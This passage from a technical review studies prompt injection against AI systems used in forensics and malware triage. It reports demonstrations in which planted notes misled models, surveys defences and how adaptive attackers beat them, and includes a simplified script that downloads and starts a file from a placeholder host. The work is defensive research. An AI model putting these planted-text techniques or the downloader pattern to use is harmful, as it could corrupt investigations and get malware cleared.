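In the first demonstration, the disk contained two photographs of rhinoceroses and a note, written to look like the output of an image classifier, that labelled the animals as triceratops. When the researchers asked the model whether any pictures in the case were classified as rhinos, it answered no and cited the note. Gemma 4 12B can interpret images, but the connection to Autopsy returned every file as text, so the model could not view the photographs.

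This result is weaker than it first appears. The answer named both photographs and mentioned the earlier label and the note, so an attentive examiner would have known what to check. The question was also about how the pictures were classified, not what they showed, so the note was directly relevant. The note combined a false claim with an instruction to disregard the old label, and the result doesn't show which one changed the answer.

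For the second demonstration, the researchers gave the agent a tool for writing files. The planted notes included an instruction to record, before reporting any findings, that the disk image was corrupt. The instruction did not name a folder, because a suspect could not know how the examiner's computer was organised. The agent used its tools to find a folder it could write to and saved the false warning there.

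The third demonstration added a tool for fetching web pages. The note described a fake quality check that required the agent to contact a web address before answering. The model did so, and the request reached the researchers' server. In a real case, such a request could alert a suspect that investigators had begun examining the disk. The model's written reasoning included the possibility that the note was an attack, but the model complied anyway, so recognizing a possible attack gives no protection unless the model or another part of the pipeline then stops.

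Each demonstration was run only once, so they show that these attacks are possible but not how often they succeed. In other trials, all three attacks also worked on Gemma 4 26B, the first worked on Ministral 3 8B, and the second and third worked on Qwen3.8 27B and gpt-oss-20b. The attacks worked less often on larger models.

Many attempts failed only because the model never opened the note or never found the photographs. Breitinger and colleagues therefore suspect that the attacks work within a narrow range of ability, where a model can find the note but cannot recognise the deception. They did not test large commercial models, so it is unclear whether any fall within that range. Commercial forensic products may also be exposed because each ships with the same prompts for every customer, so an attacker who guesses which product the police use could practise on a copy.

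### What limits on tools protect

The three attacks need different permissions, and the usual restrictions affect them very differently.

| Measure | False conclusion | File write | Network request |
|---|---|---|---|
| Only Autopsy's read-only tools | No effect | Prevents it | Prevents it |
| Writing allowed in one case folder only | No effect | Limits where the file can go | No effect |
| No network connection | No effect | No effect | Prevents it |
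| Examiner approves each tool call | No effect | Depends on the examiner | Depends on the examiner |
| Model receives the photographs | Reversed it for one of two models | No effect | No effect |

Breitinger and colleagues tested only the measure in the last row. The case for the others rests on how computers work. For network isolation, that case is as strong as an experiment, because no text in a note can make the model send a request over a connection that does not exist. Approval is weaker because, although the program that ran the model requested approval before each tool call by default, an examiner tired of the requests could allow all of them with one click.

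An agent with restricted tools can still do harm. Fetching a web page can alert the suspect, though an operator might class the tool as read-only because it changes nothing on the examiner's computer. Confining the agent to one case folder protects the rest of the computer, but a colleague would still find a false report of disk corruption in that folder and might believe it. Shah proposes sorting commands by risk, so that the system approves reading automatically, asks a human to approve changes and blocks the most dangerous commands. Santos-Grueiro's permission check, which takes a similar approach, is the best evidence that such rules can stop a misled model from acting.

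None of these restrictions stops planted text from changing the model's conclusion. This matters most in malware triage, where the attacker usually wants only a false benign verdict, which the model can give without using any tools.

Better evidence can sometimes help. When the researchers gave Gemma 4 12B the photographs, it identified a contradiction between them and the note. The other model they tested still gave the wrong answer.

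An operator can also limit the damage from a model's mistakes by using fixed rules to reduce how many cases depend on its verdict. In Canale's complete pipeline, detection software found 127 attacks in three simulated networks with no planted text, and the fixed rules left only 25 of them to Gemini 4's verdict. All 25 stayed in the analysts' queue. In three new simulated networks, however, four attacks disappeared from the queue because of the model's verdicts.

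Tests of a pipeline should measure these effects separately. *Agentic Cloud Decoys* (2026), a proposal for investigating intrusions with decoy cloud resources, recommends shortening and escaping the fields that outsiders write, then checking whether planted text appears word for word in the report, whether the model acts on it, and whether it triggers an unintended tool call. The text should appear in the report because it is evidence of an attack. If a pipeline silently deleted it, the pipeline might pass the other two checks, but the analyst would not learn that somebody had tried to mislead the model.

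## Separating instructions from sample content: design arguments and benchmark tests

Limits on tools restrict what a misled model can do. Other defences aim to stop planted instructions from misleading the model, or at least to keep them away from the part of the pipeline that makes decisions. An operator can mark the sample's text as data, choose a model trained to rank the operator's instructions above that data, or isolate the model that reads the sample. Language models have no complete solution like the one databases have for a similar problem.

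### The parametrised query

Suppose a program looks up the author of the 40-line script in the security team's database. If a careless programmer had the program paste the author's name into the text of the database command, an attacker could supply a "name" that contains further commands, and the database would run them. Programmers call this SQL injection, after SQL, the language the commands are written in.

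A parametrised query has a marked slot for the user's input, such as an author's name. It prevents SQL injection because the database parses the command before it receives the name. If the name contains commands, the database searches for an author with that name and finds no match.

According to David C, SQL injection peaked around 2010 and is now rare on websites. He suggests thinking of a language model as an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a program that an outsider tricks into using its special privileges on the outsider's behalf. Programmers can usually fix an ordinary confused deputy, but he thinks operators can only make a language model harder to trick and limit the damage. If the remaining risk is too high, he advises them to consider not using one for the job.

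Unlike a database, a triage model would still have to interpret the script and decide whether to believe the comment about a security review, even if it kept instructions and data perfectly separate.

### Marking the sample's text

The simplest defence changes only the prompt. *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting* (Hines, Lopez and colleagues, 2024) describes three versions developed at Microsoft. They would work as follows on the 40-line script.

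- With delimiters, the pipeline puts one symbol before the script and another after it, and the prompt tells the model not to obey anything in between.
- With marks throughout the data, ordinary software replaces every space in the script with an unusual character, so that the mark runs through the whole comment. The prompt explains what the character means.
- With encoding, software converts the entire script to base64, a standard way of writing any data with 64 characters. The model has to decode the script as it reads.

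The researchers tested these defences on 1,000 artificial documents, each with a planted instruction to drop the task and reply with a single keyword. They counted an attack as successful only if the model did exactly that. With GPT-3.5 Turbo and no defence, the attack worked in more than half of the summarising tests. A warning in the prompt barely helped, and delimiters cut the rate by about half. Marks throughout the text reduced it to 3.1%, and encoding reduced it to zero. In the question-answering tests, the rates were 8.0% with marks and 1.8% with encoding.

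These results are now mainly of historical interest, since the models date from 2023 or earlier. The test was also easier to score than triage would be, because a one-keyword summary is an obvious failure, while a one-word verdict of "benign" looks normal even when text in the sample caused it.

Replacing spaces with marks did not reduce GPT-3.5 Turbo's accuracy on four language benchmarks. Encoding the text in base64 reduced it sharply because the model made decoding mistakes, though GPT-4 performed well on most tasks. None of the benchmarks involved code, and Hines and colleagues warn that marks may not work well for code. Compressed JavaScript, for example, contains few spaces to replace. Base64 avoids that problem but makes a file a third longer, so a file that barely fits in the context window would no longer fit. Malware also often contains base64 already, and the model would have to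 decode those parts twice.

Researchers disagree about why marks work. Hines and colleagues meant them as a constant reminder of where the text came from, but don't know whether this explains the effect. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) describes a version that inserts a mark every eight characters into emails, which left summaries of them mostly as good as before. It attributes the benefit mainly to breaking the planted text into unusual tokens, which made the model less likely to recognise it as an instruction. If that explanation is right, marks offer little protection against the comment in the 40-line script, which contains no instruction to disrupt.

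Marks also fail if an attacker can imitate them. An attacker who learns a pipeline's delimiters can put them in a sample so that part of it seems to lie outside the marked area. Hines and colleagues therefore advise against using delimiters alone and recommend a new random mark for every request. If the mark has *k* characters and software draws each from a set of *N*, an attacker's chance of guessing it is 1 in *N* to the power *k*. Five characters from a set of 20 give 3.2 million possibilities. This protects only against forged marks, and the attacker can still try to persuade the model to obey text that carries the correct mark.

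*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested Spotlighting on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which an agent does office tasks with tools such as email and files while some of the data contains planted instructions. The benchmark's stock attacks succeeded as little as 1% of the time. An automated search that revised its text according to the defended model's responses succeeded more than 95% of the time. However, the paper describes the version it attacked as one that uses delimiters, which Hines and colleagues had already advised against, so the result is weaker evidence about versions that put marks throughout the text or encode it.

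The effect of marking also varied widely in the tests by Santos-Grueiro and by Pandey and Bhujang. Marking adds almost no overhead, so operators have little reason to leave it out, but the rest of the pipeline shouldn't depend on it.

### Training the model to rank instructions

Developers can also train a model to rank text by its source. Eric Wallace and colleagues proposed such a ranking, the instruction hierarchy, in 2024. *IH-Challenge* (Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues, 2026) describes the current version, in which OpenAI's models should rank system messages from the model's provider highest, followed by messages from the application's developer, the user's messages and then the results of tool calls.

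The rule for conflicts is exact. Let B(0) be the set of all possible answers, and let C(i) be the answers that satisfy the instructions of the source at rank i, counting from the top. Then:

B(i) = B(i−1) ∩ C(i), if at least one answer remains

B(i) = B(i−1), if none remains

Under this rule, the model should follow a lower-ranked instruction whenever it can do so without breaking a higher-ranked one. If an operator's triage prompt requires only that the answer be benign, suspicious, malicious or unknown, and a comment in the sample contains an instruction to answer "benign", the model should obey the comment, because that answer satisfies both instructions. To prevent this, the operator has to create a conflict, for example by requiring a verdict based on the code's behaviour and forbidding the model to follow instructions in the sample.

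The sample must also have a lower rank than the operator's instructions. Many pipelines combine the two in a single text. If they send that text as a developer message, the attacker's comment in the sample gets the same rank as the instructions. Delivering the sample as the result of a tool call avoids this, even in a pipeline that calls the model only once.

Guo and colleagues at OpenAI trained GPT-5-Mini to follow the hierarchy more reliably. They used reinforcement learning, in which a model tries many answers and training makes the rewarded ones more likely. A second model wrote low-ranked messages that conflicted with higher-ranked instructions, tried them on the current version of GPT-5-Mini and revised them. The tasks were simple enough for a short program to grade, such as keeping a PIN secret. Some tasks only looked forbidden, so that the model could not do well by refusing everything.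 Excessive refusal would be a serious problem in triage, and without those tasks the average helpfulness score on safety tests fell from 77% to 61%.

Training increased the share of planted-instruction attacks that GPT-5-Mini resisted from 44% to 100% on OpenAI's internal benchmark, but only from 88% to 91% on CyberSecEval 2, a public benchmark. The training left scores on difficult science questions unchanged but slightly reduced the quality of ordinary chat. GPT-5-Mini gave a better answer than an older OpenAI model 71% of the time before training and 66% afterwards.

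### StruQ and SecAlign

Researchers outside the commercial laboratories have developed similar training for open models. *StruQ* (2024) combines it with a filter, ordinary software that places reserved separators between the instructions and the data and deletes any copies of those separators from the data. The developers then train the model to follow instructions in the proper place and ignore those in the data, using examples of both.

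The filter provides part of the protection of a parametrised query, since the attacker can't insert a real separator. But a database is certain to enforce the boundary, while StruQ's model has only learned to follow it from examples. Even so, *May I have your Attention?* (2025) puts the success rate of known hand-written attacks on StruQ close to zero.

*SecAlign* (2024) trains the model on pairs of answers. In one example given by Chen, Zharmagambetov and colleagues (2025), in *Meta-SecAlign*, the user asks for a recipe for the dish named in the data. The data contains the word "omelette" and a stray question about the history of yoga. The good answer is an omelette recipe, and the bad answer is about yoga. For each pair, training reduces this quantity:

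Loss = −log σ(β × [r(good) − r(bad)])

Here r is the logarithm of the ratio between the probability that the trained model gives an answer and the probability that the original model gives it. The function σ converts the difference between r for the good answer and r for the bad one to a number between 0 and 1, and β sets how strongly that difference counts. The loss falls as the trained model becomes more likely than the original to give the good answer and less likely to give the bad one. The comparison with the original also discourages changes unrelated to planted instructions.

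When Chen and colleagues applied this method to a larger model, Llama 3.3 70B, it became secure but completed only 6.2% of AgentDojo's agent tasks, down from 59.8%. The training examples always placed the stray instruction at the end of the data, so the model learned to ignore whatever instruction came last, even when it was the user's own request. The new method, Meta-SecAlign, places about half of the stray instructions at the beginning instead. It also trains on answers written by the original model, so that training does not needlessly change the model's style.

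| Model | Tasks completed without attacks (AgentDojo) | Attack success (AgentDojo) | Attack success (SEP) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 59.8% | 14.7% | 99.7% |
| Same, with SecAlign | 6.2% | 0% | 12.4% |
| Same, with Meta-SecAlign | 84.5% | 1.9% | 4.0% |
| Qwen3.6 27B | 89.7% | 26.7% | 98.9% |
| Same, with Meta-SecAlign | 87.6% | 2.2% | 6.4% |
| GPT-5 | 80.4% | 0.2% | 52.6% |
| Gemini 3 Pro | 92.8% | 2.3% | 74.6% |

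Only Llama 3.3 shows the rise to 84.5%, and Chen and colleagues can't fully explain it. Qwen's small loss is more typical. The defended models cost no more to run than the originals, but an operator who relies on a commercial model can't train it this way.

The last column is the most relevant to triage. AgentDojo tests whether planted text makes an agent take an unwanted action with its tools. SEP tests whether a model responds to a stray instruction in a passage it is working on, which is closer to a single call that returns a verdict. GPT-5 and Gemini 3 Pro almost never took the unwanted action in AgentDojo but followed most of the stray instructions in SEP, so a low attack success rate on an agent benchmark is poor evidence that a model will ignore instructions in a script. Their developers may have concentrated on agents, where following planted instructions does more damage.

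Both commercial models are also older than the models on sale in late 2026. The closest evidence on a newer model comes from Canale's small test, in which Gemini 4 resisted fixed text resembling instructions but was misled by at least one false story.

Training a model to ignore instructions in data does not seem to make it overlook them as evidence, as analysts might fear. Chen and colleagues asked models to rewrite sentences that contained instructions without carrying them out. The original Llama model did so correctly 19.8% of the time and the Meta-SecAlign version 78.9%. A model with this training should therefore be better able to report that a sample contains an order to an AI scanner.

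### When attackers adapt to the defence

Most of the figures above come from fixed sets of attacks written without knowledge of the defence. Nasr and colleagues, from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and several universities, tested 12 published defences against attackers who knew the defence they were attacking. They used automated methods that repeatedly proposed a text, scored the defended model's response and kept what worked best, and they also ran a competition with more than 500 human participants. The original papers reported attack success near zero for most of the defences, but the success rate of these adaptive attacks exceeded 90% for most of them.

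The trained models did no better than the marked prompts. The attack on StruQ succeeded in every case the researchers tried, often by making the planted text resemble a message from a trusted source. On AgentDojo, the success rate of attacks on Meta-SecAlign rose from 2% to 96%. Chen and colleagues report a lower rate, 47.1%, from a different adaptive attack on a different benchmark, where the undefended model's rate was 98.1%. They say their method does not solve the problem.

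Guo and colleagues' training held up better, perhaps because their attacker model kept adapting throughout. They paid 127 people to attack the models, with bounties for success. The testers succeeded on 36.2% of assigned tasks against the original GPT-5-Mini and on 11.7% against the trained version. When a second copy of the model checked each answer for violations, the rate fell to 7.1%. Only 0.4% of attempts against the trained model without the checker succeeded, but the testers averaged 52 attempts per task. In a separate test, an automated attacker trained against a frozen copy of the model. It had little success at first but kept improving, more slowly when the checker was present.

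These tests give the attacker advantages that a malware author may not have. Nasr and colleagues deliberately assumed an attacker with plenty of computing power and many attempts. A malware author who can't see a private pipeline's verdicts can still practise on a copy of a model the pipeline is likely to use, but can't be sure the attack will work on the pipeline itself.

However, the author only has to do this work once. Text that misleads a widely used model could go into hundreds of samples, just as different actors copied the FRUITSHELL comment. But defenders could then find every exact copy with an ordinary YARA rule. Adaptive attacks are therefore most worrying in the first samples that carry a new text, before anyone has written a rule for it.

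Nasr and colleagues argue that testing can show that a defence fails but cannot show that it is secure, however many attacks it withstands. They also point out that weak defences can be worth having because they stop unskilled attackers, who wrote most of the misleading text that researchers have found in real malware so far. Stopping skilled attackers requires a design that remains safe even when the model follows instructions in a sample.

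### Isolating the model that reads the sample

In April 2023 the programmer Simon Willison proposed the dual-model pattern, in which the model that planted text might take over has no access to anything it could misuse. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) includes this pattern among six designs. The pattern has three parts.

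1. A privileged model receives the operator's task, plans the work and can use tools. It never sees any text from the sample.
2. A quarantined model reads the sample and answers questions about it. It has no tools.
3. Ordinary software, called the orchestrator, carries requests between them. It stores each of the quarantined model's answers under a label, and the privileged model sees only the label.

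If the operator wants every web address in the 40-line script checked against a list of known malicious servers, the privileged model requests the addresses and receives the label ADDRESSES. It then requests a check of ADDRESSES, and the orchestrator inserts the real addresses when it calls the checking tool. Planted text in the script could make the quarantined model return a false address, but it couldn't reach the privileged model and make it skip the check.

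CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues at Google and ETH Zurich published in 2025, extends the pattern. The privileged model writes a complete program for the task before the sample is opened, and ordinary software runs it. The program can call tools and quarantined models, and security policies limit where their data may go. Text in the sample can't add a step to the program, but it can still change the values that the steps use, as Beurer-Kellner and colleagues note about this design. In their example, text planted in a calendar can change what an email says but not who receives it.

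A planner that sees only labels can't react to what the sample contains, but malware analysis often requires this. An analyst who finds a packed section unpacks it, and one who finds a web address looks it up. In *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) therefore let the quarantined model return whole numbers, decimal numbers, yes-or-no answers and choices from a list written by the operator, but no free text. None of the permitted types can contain an instruction. The researchers tested the idea on three agents.

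| Agent | Tasks completed, undefended | Tasks completed, isolated | Attack success, undefended | Attack success, isolated |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Online shopping | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
| Calendar scheduling | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| Bug fixing | 68.3% | 45.0% | 98.9% | 0% |

The zero attack success rates follow from the design, so a cleverer attacker wouldn't change them. Jacob and colleagues ran the attacks only to confirm that they had built the agents correctly. An argument from the design is much stronger evidence than a low attack success rate on a benchmark, but it covers less here because they define prompt injection as text that diverts a model from its task and explicitly exclude text that misleads it with false information.

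How much isolation reduces an agent's performance depends on the task. Scheduling a meeting needs only a list of times, and the isolated agent did just as well. Fixing a bug depends on the description in the bug report, but the isolated agent received only file names, line numbers and categories, and it succeeded about a third less often. Investigating an unknown program is probably closer to fixing a bug, since an operator can't list in advance every behaviour that might matter. The isolated bug fixer was also expensive to run because it used four models, one to investigate the report, one to write three plans, one to choose among them and one to make the repair.

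Some designs allow a little text. For an agent that reads documentation, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest a strict format with limits such as 30 characters for a function name. *Twin Agent* (2026), a more recent design, uses the observation that attacks on the strongest models seem to need fairly long text. A short field could be a reasonable compromise for the names of files or imported functions. However, it offers no proof of security, and a false claim such as "Signed by Microsoft" takes only 19 characters.

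*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) uses computer-checked proofs to establish what such designs guarantee. It compares an agent with an imaginary twin that follows the same plan under the same restrictions but never obeys text from outsiders. The agent is secure if planted text can't make it reveal anything that the twin wouldn't also reveal in response to some input. The paper proves that an agent is secure if, by the time it first reads untrusted content, it has permanently lost every tool that planted text could call. If it loses them even one step later, it may already have leaked something. The proof assumes that each planted instruction triggers a single call and that whether the model obeys doesn't depend on secret data.

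The theorem would cover an agent that reads a company's private records and then opens a hostile script. It doesn't cover an agent such as Project Ire, which chooses each step as it goes, because Dongol's comparison requires a plan fixed beforehand. The theorem also concerns only leaks. Dongol notes that in the dual-model pattern, planted text can only corrupt an answer. That is a minor problem in most of the applications that he and the other researchers discuss.

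### Why isolation does not protect the verdict

In triage, the attacker usually wants only to corrupt the answer. Suppose a quarantined model reads the 40-line script and returns three values: whether the script downloads a program, whether it starts one, and a verdict. The planted comment can't make the pipeline delete a file, contact a server or skip the next sample, but it can still lead the model to return "benign". The orchestrator then passes on that verdict because it is on the list of approved values, and the script clears triage.

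Beurer-Kellner and colleagues recognise this kind of limit in other settings. One example is an agent that sorts invoices from other files, using a separate model for each file. A hostile file can't affect how the agent treats the others, but it can cause the agent to classify it as an invoice. They consider this acceptable because the attacker could achieve the same thing by sending a real invoice. They make a similar point about an assistant that ranks job applicants, where an applicant can use a dishonest CV to improve their own position but can't lower anyone else's.

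That reasoning fails for malware, because an attacker benefits only when a harmful program gets a benign verdict, which requires deceiving the system. The attacker could get the same verdict honestly by submitting a harmless program, but would gain nothing from it.

Most triage pipelines already have much of the protection that isolation offers. A pipeline that calls a model once, gives it no tools and accepts only a verdict from a fixed list is in effect using a quarantined model. Gemini 2.5 Pro worked under almost these conditions, and false product descriptions written by Choi and colleagues still misled it. Replacing the verdict with narrower questions doesn't necessarily help either. In *MARS*, planted text removed alerts even when Gemini 2.5 Flash only listed a program's behaviours.

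Isolation is still worthwhile in parts of a triage system. Reading each sample in a separate request keeps one hostile file from influencing the verdicts on others, which can happen when a pipeline judges several files together to save money. Isolation also protects agents with access to private data or powerful tools. It matters too where one model's free-text explanation goes to a second model, because the explanation can contain planted text. The pipeline can avoid that by sending the second model only the fixed fields and keeping the explanation for human analysts.

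Dividing a single sample among separate quarantined models might partly protect the verdict. If each model judged only a few lines of the script, the one that read the lines that download and start the second program wouldn't see the comment at the top. The verdict would then depend on how the pipeline combined the models' answers. Jacob and colleagues' shopping agent takes the median of the scores for a product's reviews, so one dishonest review has little effect. A malware pipeline would have to use the worst score, because one harmful function is enough to make a program malicious. This would probably cause more false alarms, since many harmless installers contain lines that look suspicious on their own. An attacker could also repeat the comment next to the harmful lines.

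David C mentions a stricter principle, which came out of an online discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista. When a model processes information from some party, its privileges should drop to those of that party. People usually apply this to tools, so that a model reading a stranger's email can't do anything the operator wouldn't let the stranger do. In triage, the principle would also apply to verdicts. A sample's author has no authority to declare it safe, so a model that has read the sample shouldn't either. The model could raise an alarm or escalate the file, but clearing the file would require evidence from another source.

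Under this rule, planted text could at most stop the model from raising an extra alarm. Microsoft's plans for Project Ire show that a model can be useful as an extra alarm even if it misses most malware. The rule would create a lot of work for a team that uses a model mainly to shorten its queue, because some other check would have to clear every harmless program.

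## Filtering and selecting what the model reads

Ordinary software can keep some of the attacker's text from reaching the model. The evidence builder can remove text that the program doesn't need, search the rest for text aimed at AI systems, and choose which parts of a large program to send. Removal doesn't depend on the model's judgement, because the model never receives the removed text.

### Comments and names

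Cut down to five lines, with simplified function names, the invented install script might look like this:

```
/* (comment claiming that a security team approved this file) */
const approvedUrl = "https://files.example/helper";
const approvedFile = tempFolder() + "/helper";
download(approvedUrl, approvedFile);
start(approvedFile);
```

After filtering, the model would receive this:

```
const name1 = "https://files.example/helper";
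const name2 = tempFolder() + "/helper";
download(name1, name2);
start(name2);
```

The comment is gone, and so are the variable names that repeated its claim. The model still gets the web address and the order of the steps, which is enough to recognise a downloader. The evidence builder should rename only what the script defines. If it also renamed `download` and `start`, which belong to the system, the model could no longer tell what the script does.

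Stripping comments with a simple search pattern can also delete evidence. In JavaScript, two slashes begin a comment that runs to the end of the line, so a simple pattern deletes the slashes and everything after them. Web addresses also contain two slashes, so the pattern would cut an address off after `https:` and remove what may be the best clue in the script. An attacker could exploit this mistake by putting comment markers inside strings so that the stripper deletes real code.

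A parser avoids the mistake because it applies the language's grammar from the top of the file. It has already passed an opening quotation mark when it reaches the slashes, so it treats them as part of a string. *CodeSentinel* (Cheng, Yu and colleagues, 2026) uses a parser called Tree-sitter to find the comments, strings, names and decoy blocks in code that a coding assistant is about to read, then scores them in three stages.

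1. Rules look for phrases that resemble instructions, for invisible characters, and for conspicuous blocks that the program hardly uses.
2. A small local model measures how improbable the text of each remaining piece is, which exposes the odd strings that optimisation algorithms produce.
3. The software replaces a piece with something neutral and measures how much the local model's answer changes. A large change suggests that the piece was steering the answer.

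The software cleans only the model's copy of the code. Signature tools and sandboxes need the original, because malware can hide data in a comment and read its own file to get it back.

On three commercial models, CodeSentinel reduced the attack success rate from 18–27% to 6–8%. It also damaged some harmless code, and the success rate on one set of programming exercises fell by six percentage points. Attackers who knew the design did better by planting several copies of the same text. Removing one copy then no longer changed the answer much, and the detection score fell from 0.82 to 0.62, where 1 is perfect.

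Cheng and colleagues did not test CodeSentinel on malware, and its last stage would suit malware analysis poorly because the piece of a sample that changes the verdict most may be the real evidence. For example, replacing the web address in the install script could easily change the verdict from "malicious" to "suspicious", and CodeSentinel might then remove the address as a manipulation.

Removing every comment is cruder but harder to evade, because an attacker can't get a comment through by rewording it. Wu and Nita-Rotaru reject this option because earlier research found that comments help models find vulnerabilities. That reason is weaker in malware triage, where the attacker may have written the comments, and Thornton's tests also gave little reason to keep them.

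Wu and Nita-Rotaru also tested a compromise, in which the detector first analyses the code without comments in a separate request and then receives the full version along with that analysis. Their adaptive attacker's success rate fell from 91% to zero on one detector and from over 95% to about 50% on two others. On the fourth, a system in which several models debate the verdict, it only fell from 100% to 96%, because later contributions to the debate could overturn the first analysis. A triage pipeline could prevent such reversals with a fixed rule that comments may only make a verdict more severe.

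### Disguised characters and unused sections

Unicode contains letters that look identical, such as the Latin and Cyrillic "a", and characters with no width. Attackers can use them to disguise a phrase so that a keyword rule misses it, though a model may still interpret it correctly. Standard normalisation converts variants such as full-width letters to their ordinary forms, but it doesn't change Cyrillic letters or zero-width spaces. The evidence builder therefore also needs a table of look-alikes and a step that deletes invisible characters. Replacing look-alikes would garble genuine Russian text, so it makes sense to do this only in a copy used for matching, and to record what changed.

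Normalisation probably helps keyword rules more than it helps trained detectors. *PIDS-Bench* (Shire and Kim, 2026) tested four ready-made detectors on 405 attacks disguised with look-alikes, invisible characters or digits in place of letters. Three of the detectors caught a slightly higher share of these than of attacks in general, and the fourth caught 32% of these compared with 37% of attacks in general.

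Compiled programs have no comments to remove, and their strings are much harder to do without because a string may be a server address, a command or the text of a ransom note. The evidence builder could drop only the strings that no code refers to, which would have removed the false product description that Choi and colleagues put in an unused section. But programs often calculate a string's location while they run, so a static tool will wrongly mark some important strings as unused. An attacker can also add a harmless instruction that refers to the planted text. It would be safer to keep every string and tell the model which ones the code appears to use.

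Metadata presents the same difficulty. Sava and colleagues tested a cheap Gemini model on 200 Windows programs, half of them malware. Given only code, the model wrongly flagged 56 of the 100 harmless programs. When it also had metadata such as file headers, import tables and embedded resources, it wrongly flagged 30. The number of malicious programs it missed barely changed, from 10 to 11. Metadata thus mainly led the model to clear programs it would otherwise have flagged, which is the effect a forger wants, but an operator who removed it would get nearly twice as many false alarms.

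### Rules and trained classifiers

An operator can also search for text that seems to address an AI, instead of removing text by its location. A YARA rule can find exact copies of a known comment, but general rules are much less reliable. As a baseline, Shire and Kim wrote a simple set of rules to detect orders to ignore instructions, requests for the system prompt, role-play and signs of encoding. They compared these rules with ready-made classifiers, which are smaller models trained to recognise attacks or unsafe text.

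| Detector | Attacks caught | Harmless security-related prompts flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Keyword rules | 3.5% | 22.9% |
| ProtectAI | 85.8% | 21.6% |
| DeBERTa-PI | 94.4% | 80.4% |
| Prompt Guard 2 | 36.9% | 15.2% |
| Llama Guard 3 1B | 42.0% | 18.0% |

The harmless prompts covered subjects such as security, system prompts and model behaviour but contained no attempt at manipulation. The keyword rules flagged them far more often than they flagged real attacks, but raised no false alarms on ordinary text. Shire and Kim chose the prompts to be difficult, so the last column does not predict results on everyday files. A malware team could still see many false alarms, because its files include many security tools.

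Shire and Kim also trained their own detectors. The best was almost perfect on ordinary test data but flagged 38% of the difficult harmless prompts. Raising the alarm threshold didn't solve the problem, because in one training run the detector gave about a third of those prompts a score of at least 0.9 out of 1. Adding difficult harmless examples to the training data nearly eliminated false alarms on prompts the researchers had written, but many remained on prompts from public collections. A team that trains a detector on examples it invented could easily overestimate how well the detector works.

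Formatting also caused false positives. When the researchers wrapped difficult harmless prompts in JSON (a common data format), padded them with other text or put an official-looking prefix in front, their best detector wrongly flagged 81% of them. Many evidence builders produce JSON, so their output could be wrongly flagged too.

The catch rates depend heavily on the test. *When Benchmarks Lie* (2026) reports that a ProtectAI detector caught only 8% of instructions planted in data, with a false-alarm rate of 4.2%, while one from Deepset caught 99.8% but had a false-alarm rate of 82.4%. Many of Shire and Kim's attacks came from a collection of prompts typed directly to chatbots, which probably explains why ProtectAI's detector did so much better in their test. Results for a general-purpose model used as a detector also varied widely across four versions of its prompt, from 11% to 93% of planted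 instructions caught, with false-alarm rates between 1.4% and 18.9%.

Detectors have even more trouble with long inputs. In Liu and colleagues' benchmark of long documents, a ProtectAI detector missed every planted message. On the code-review task, Prompt Guard 2 missed only 5% of planted messages but flagged 73% of clean inputs. PIShield, which examines a model's internal signals, did best on that task, missing 13% with no false alarms, but it missed 85% on emails.

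False alarms can be much rarer on ordinary text. *LLMail-Inject* (2025) tested four detectors on 1,000 real business emails. Their false alarm rates ranged from zero to 5.7%, and 10% of the emails set off at least one detector. *Securing AI Agents Against Prompt Injection Attacks* (2025) reports a 5.7% false alarm rate for a complete set of defences. Most of those false alarms came from text that reads like instructions, such as technical documentation.

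Even false-alarm rates like these are high for a service as large as VirusTotal, which receives two million samples a day. If one in a million samples contained planted text, about two files a day would contain it, while a detector with a 1% false-alarm rate would wrongly flag some 20,000 files that had none.

### DataSentinel

*DataSentinel* (Liu, Jia and colleagues, 2025) looks for planted instructions by giving a separate model a small task along with the sample and checking whether the model still does the task.

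1. Ordinary software generates a random key of seven characters.
2. It asks the detection model to repeat the key and ignore the text that follows, then attaches the sample.
3. If the key appears in the reply, the software treats the sample as clean. If not, it assumes that the model followed an instruction in the sample, and flags it.

This works best with a model that is easy to distract, so the researchers trained theirs to be more vulnerable to planted text. They alternated between searching for text that the current model failed to detect and training the model to fail to repeat the key when it read such text. They also trained it to repeat the key when it read clean text.

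On short texts such as single sentences and phone messages, DataSentinel's main version wrongly flagged at most 1% of clean inputs and missed at most 7% of existing attacks. Each check took about 1.6 seconds. In the long-document benchmark, DataSentinel caught every planted message in the code reviews but also flagged 54% of the clean reviews and all of the clean academic papers. A model trained to be distractible may lose track of the key in a long document. Most malware samples are closer in length to those documents than to a phone message.

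*How Not to Detect Prompt Injections with an LLM* (2025) describes a flaw in the method behind this kind of test that lets a handwritten attack evade it reliably.

For triage, DataSentinel's most important failure occurred when the attacker wanted the model to do its normal job but get the wrong answer. In one test, the application and the planted text both involved judging whether a text was positive or negative. DataSentinel missed 87% of these attacks when the attacker adapted to it, compared with at most 6% for other applications. Liu, Jia and colleagues explain that such an attacker doesn't need an instruction, because misleading data is enough and gives the detection model no competing task to follow.

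The comment in the install script is misleading data of this kind. A detection model could repeat the key and ignore the comment as asked, and DataSentinel would then report the file as clean. Keyword rules and classifiers trained on commands can also miss this kind of text. A classifier trained to flag claims of safety would catch the comment, but it would also flag a lot of legitimate software, because developers routinely describe what their software does and who checked it.

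### Keeping the text as evidence

When a detector finds an instruction to an AI scanner, deleting it would lose a useful clue, because few legitimate install scripts have any reason to tell a scanner what verdict to return. The evidence builder can instead save the text and its position for a human analyst. To keep the attacker's wording out of the model's input, it can give the model only a fixed label, such as "text addressed to an AI system, in a comment".

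Such a search also turns up harmless files other than legitimate AI applications. A security researcher's project may include a collection of known attacks, and a scanner's test files contain planted text so that its developers can check that it works. A set of YARA rules for finding such text will also match the file that contains the rules.

The location of a prompt helps to distinguish an AI application's own prompts from text meant to mislead a scanner. A parser can show that a prompt is in a string that the program sends to an AI provider, as expected in an AI application. Attackers can imitate this, so it shouldn't clear a file. A comment at the top of an install script that gives orders to a scanner serves no such purpose, and is a good reason to escalate the file. No detector in these studies is accurate enough for its alarm alone to justify a malicious verdict.

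### Choosing which functions to read

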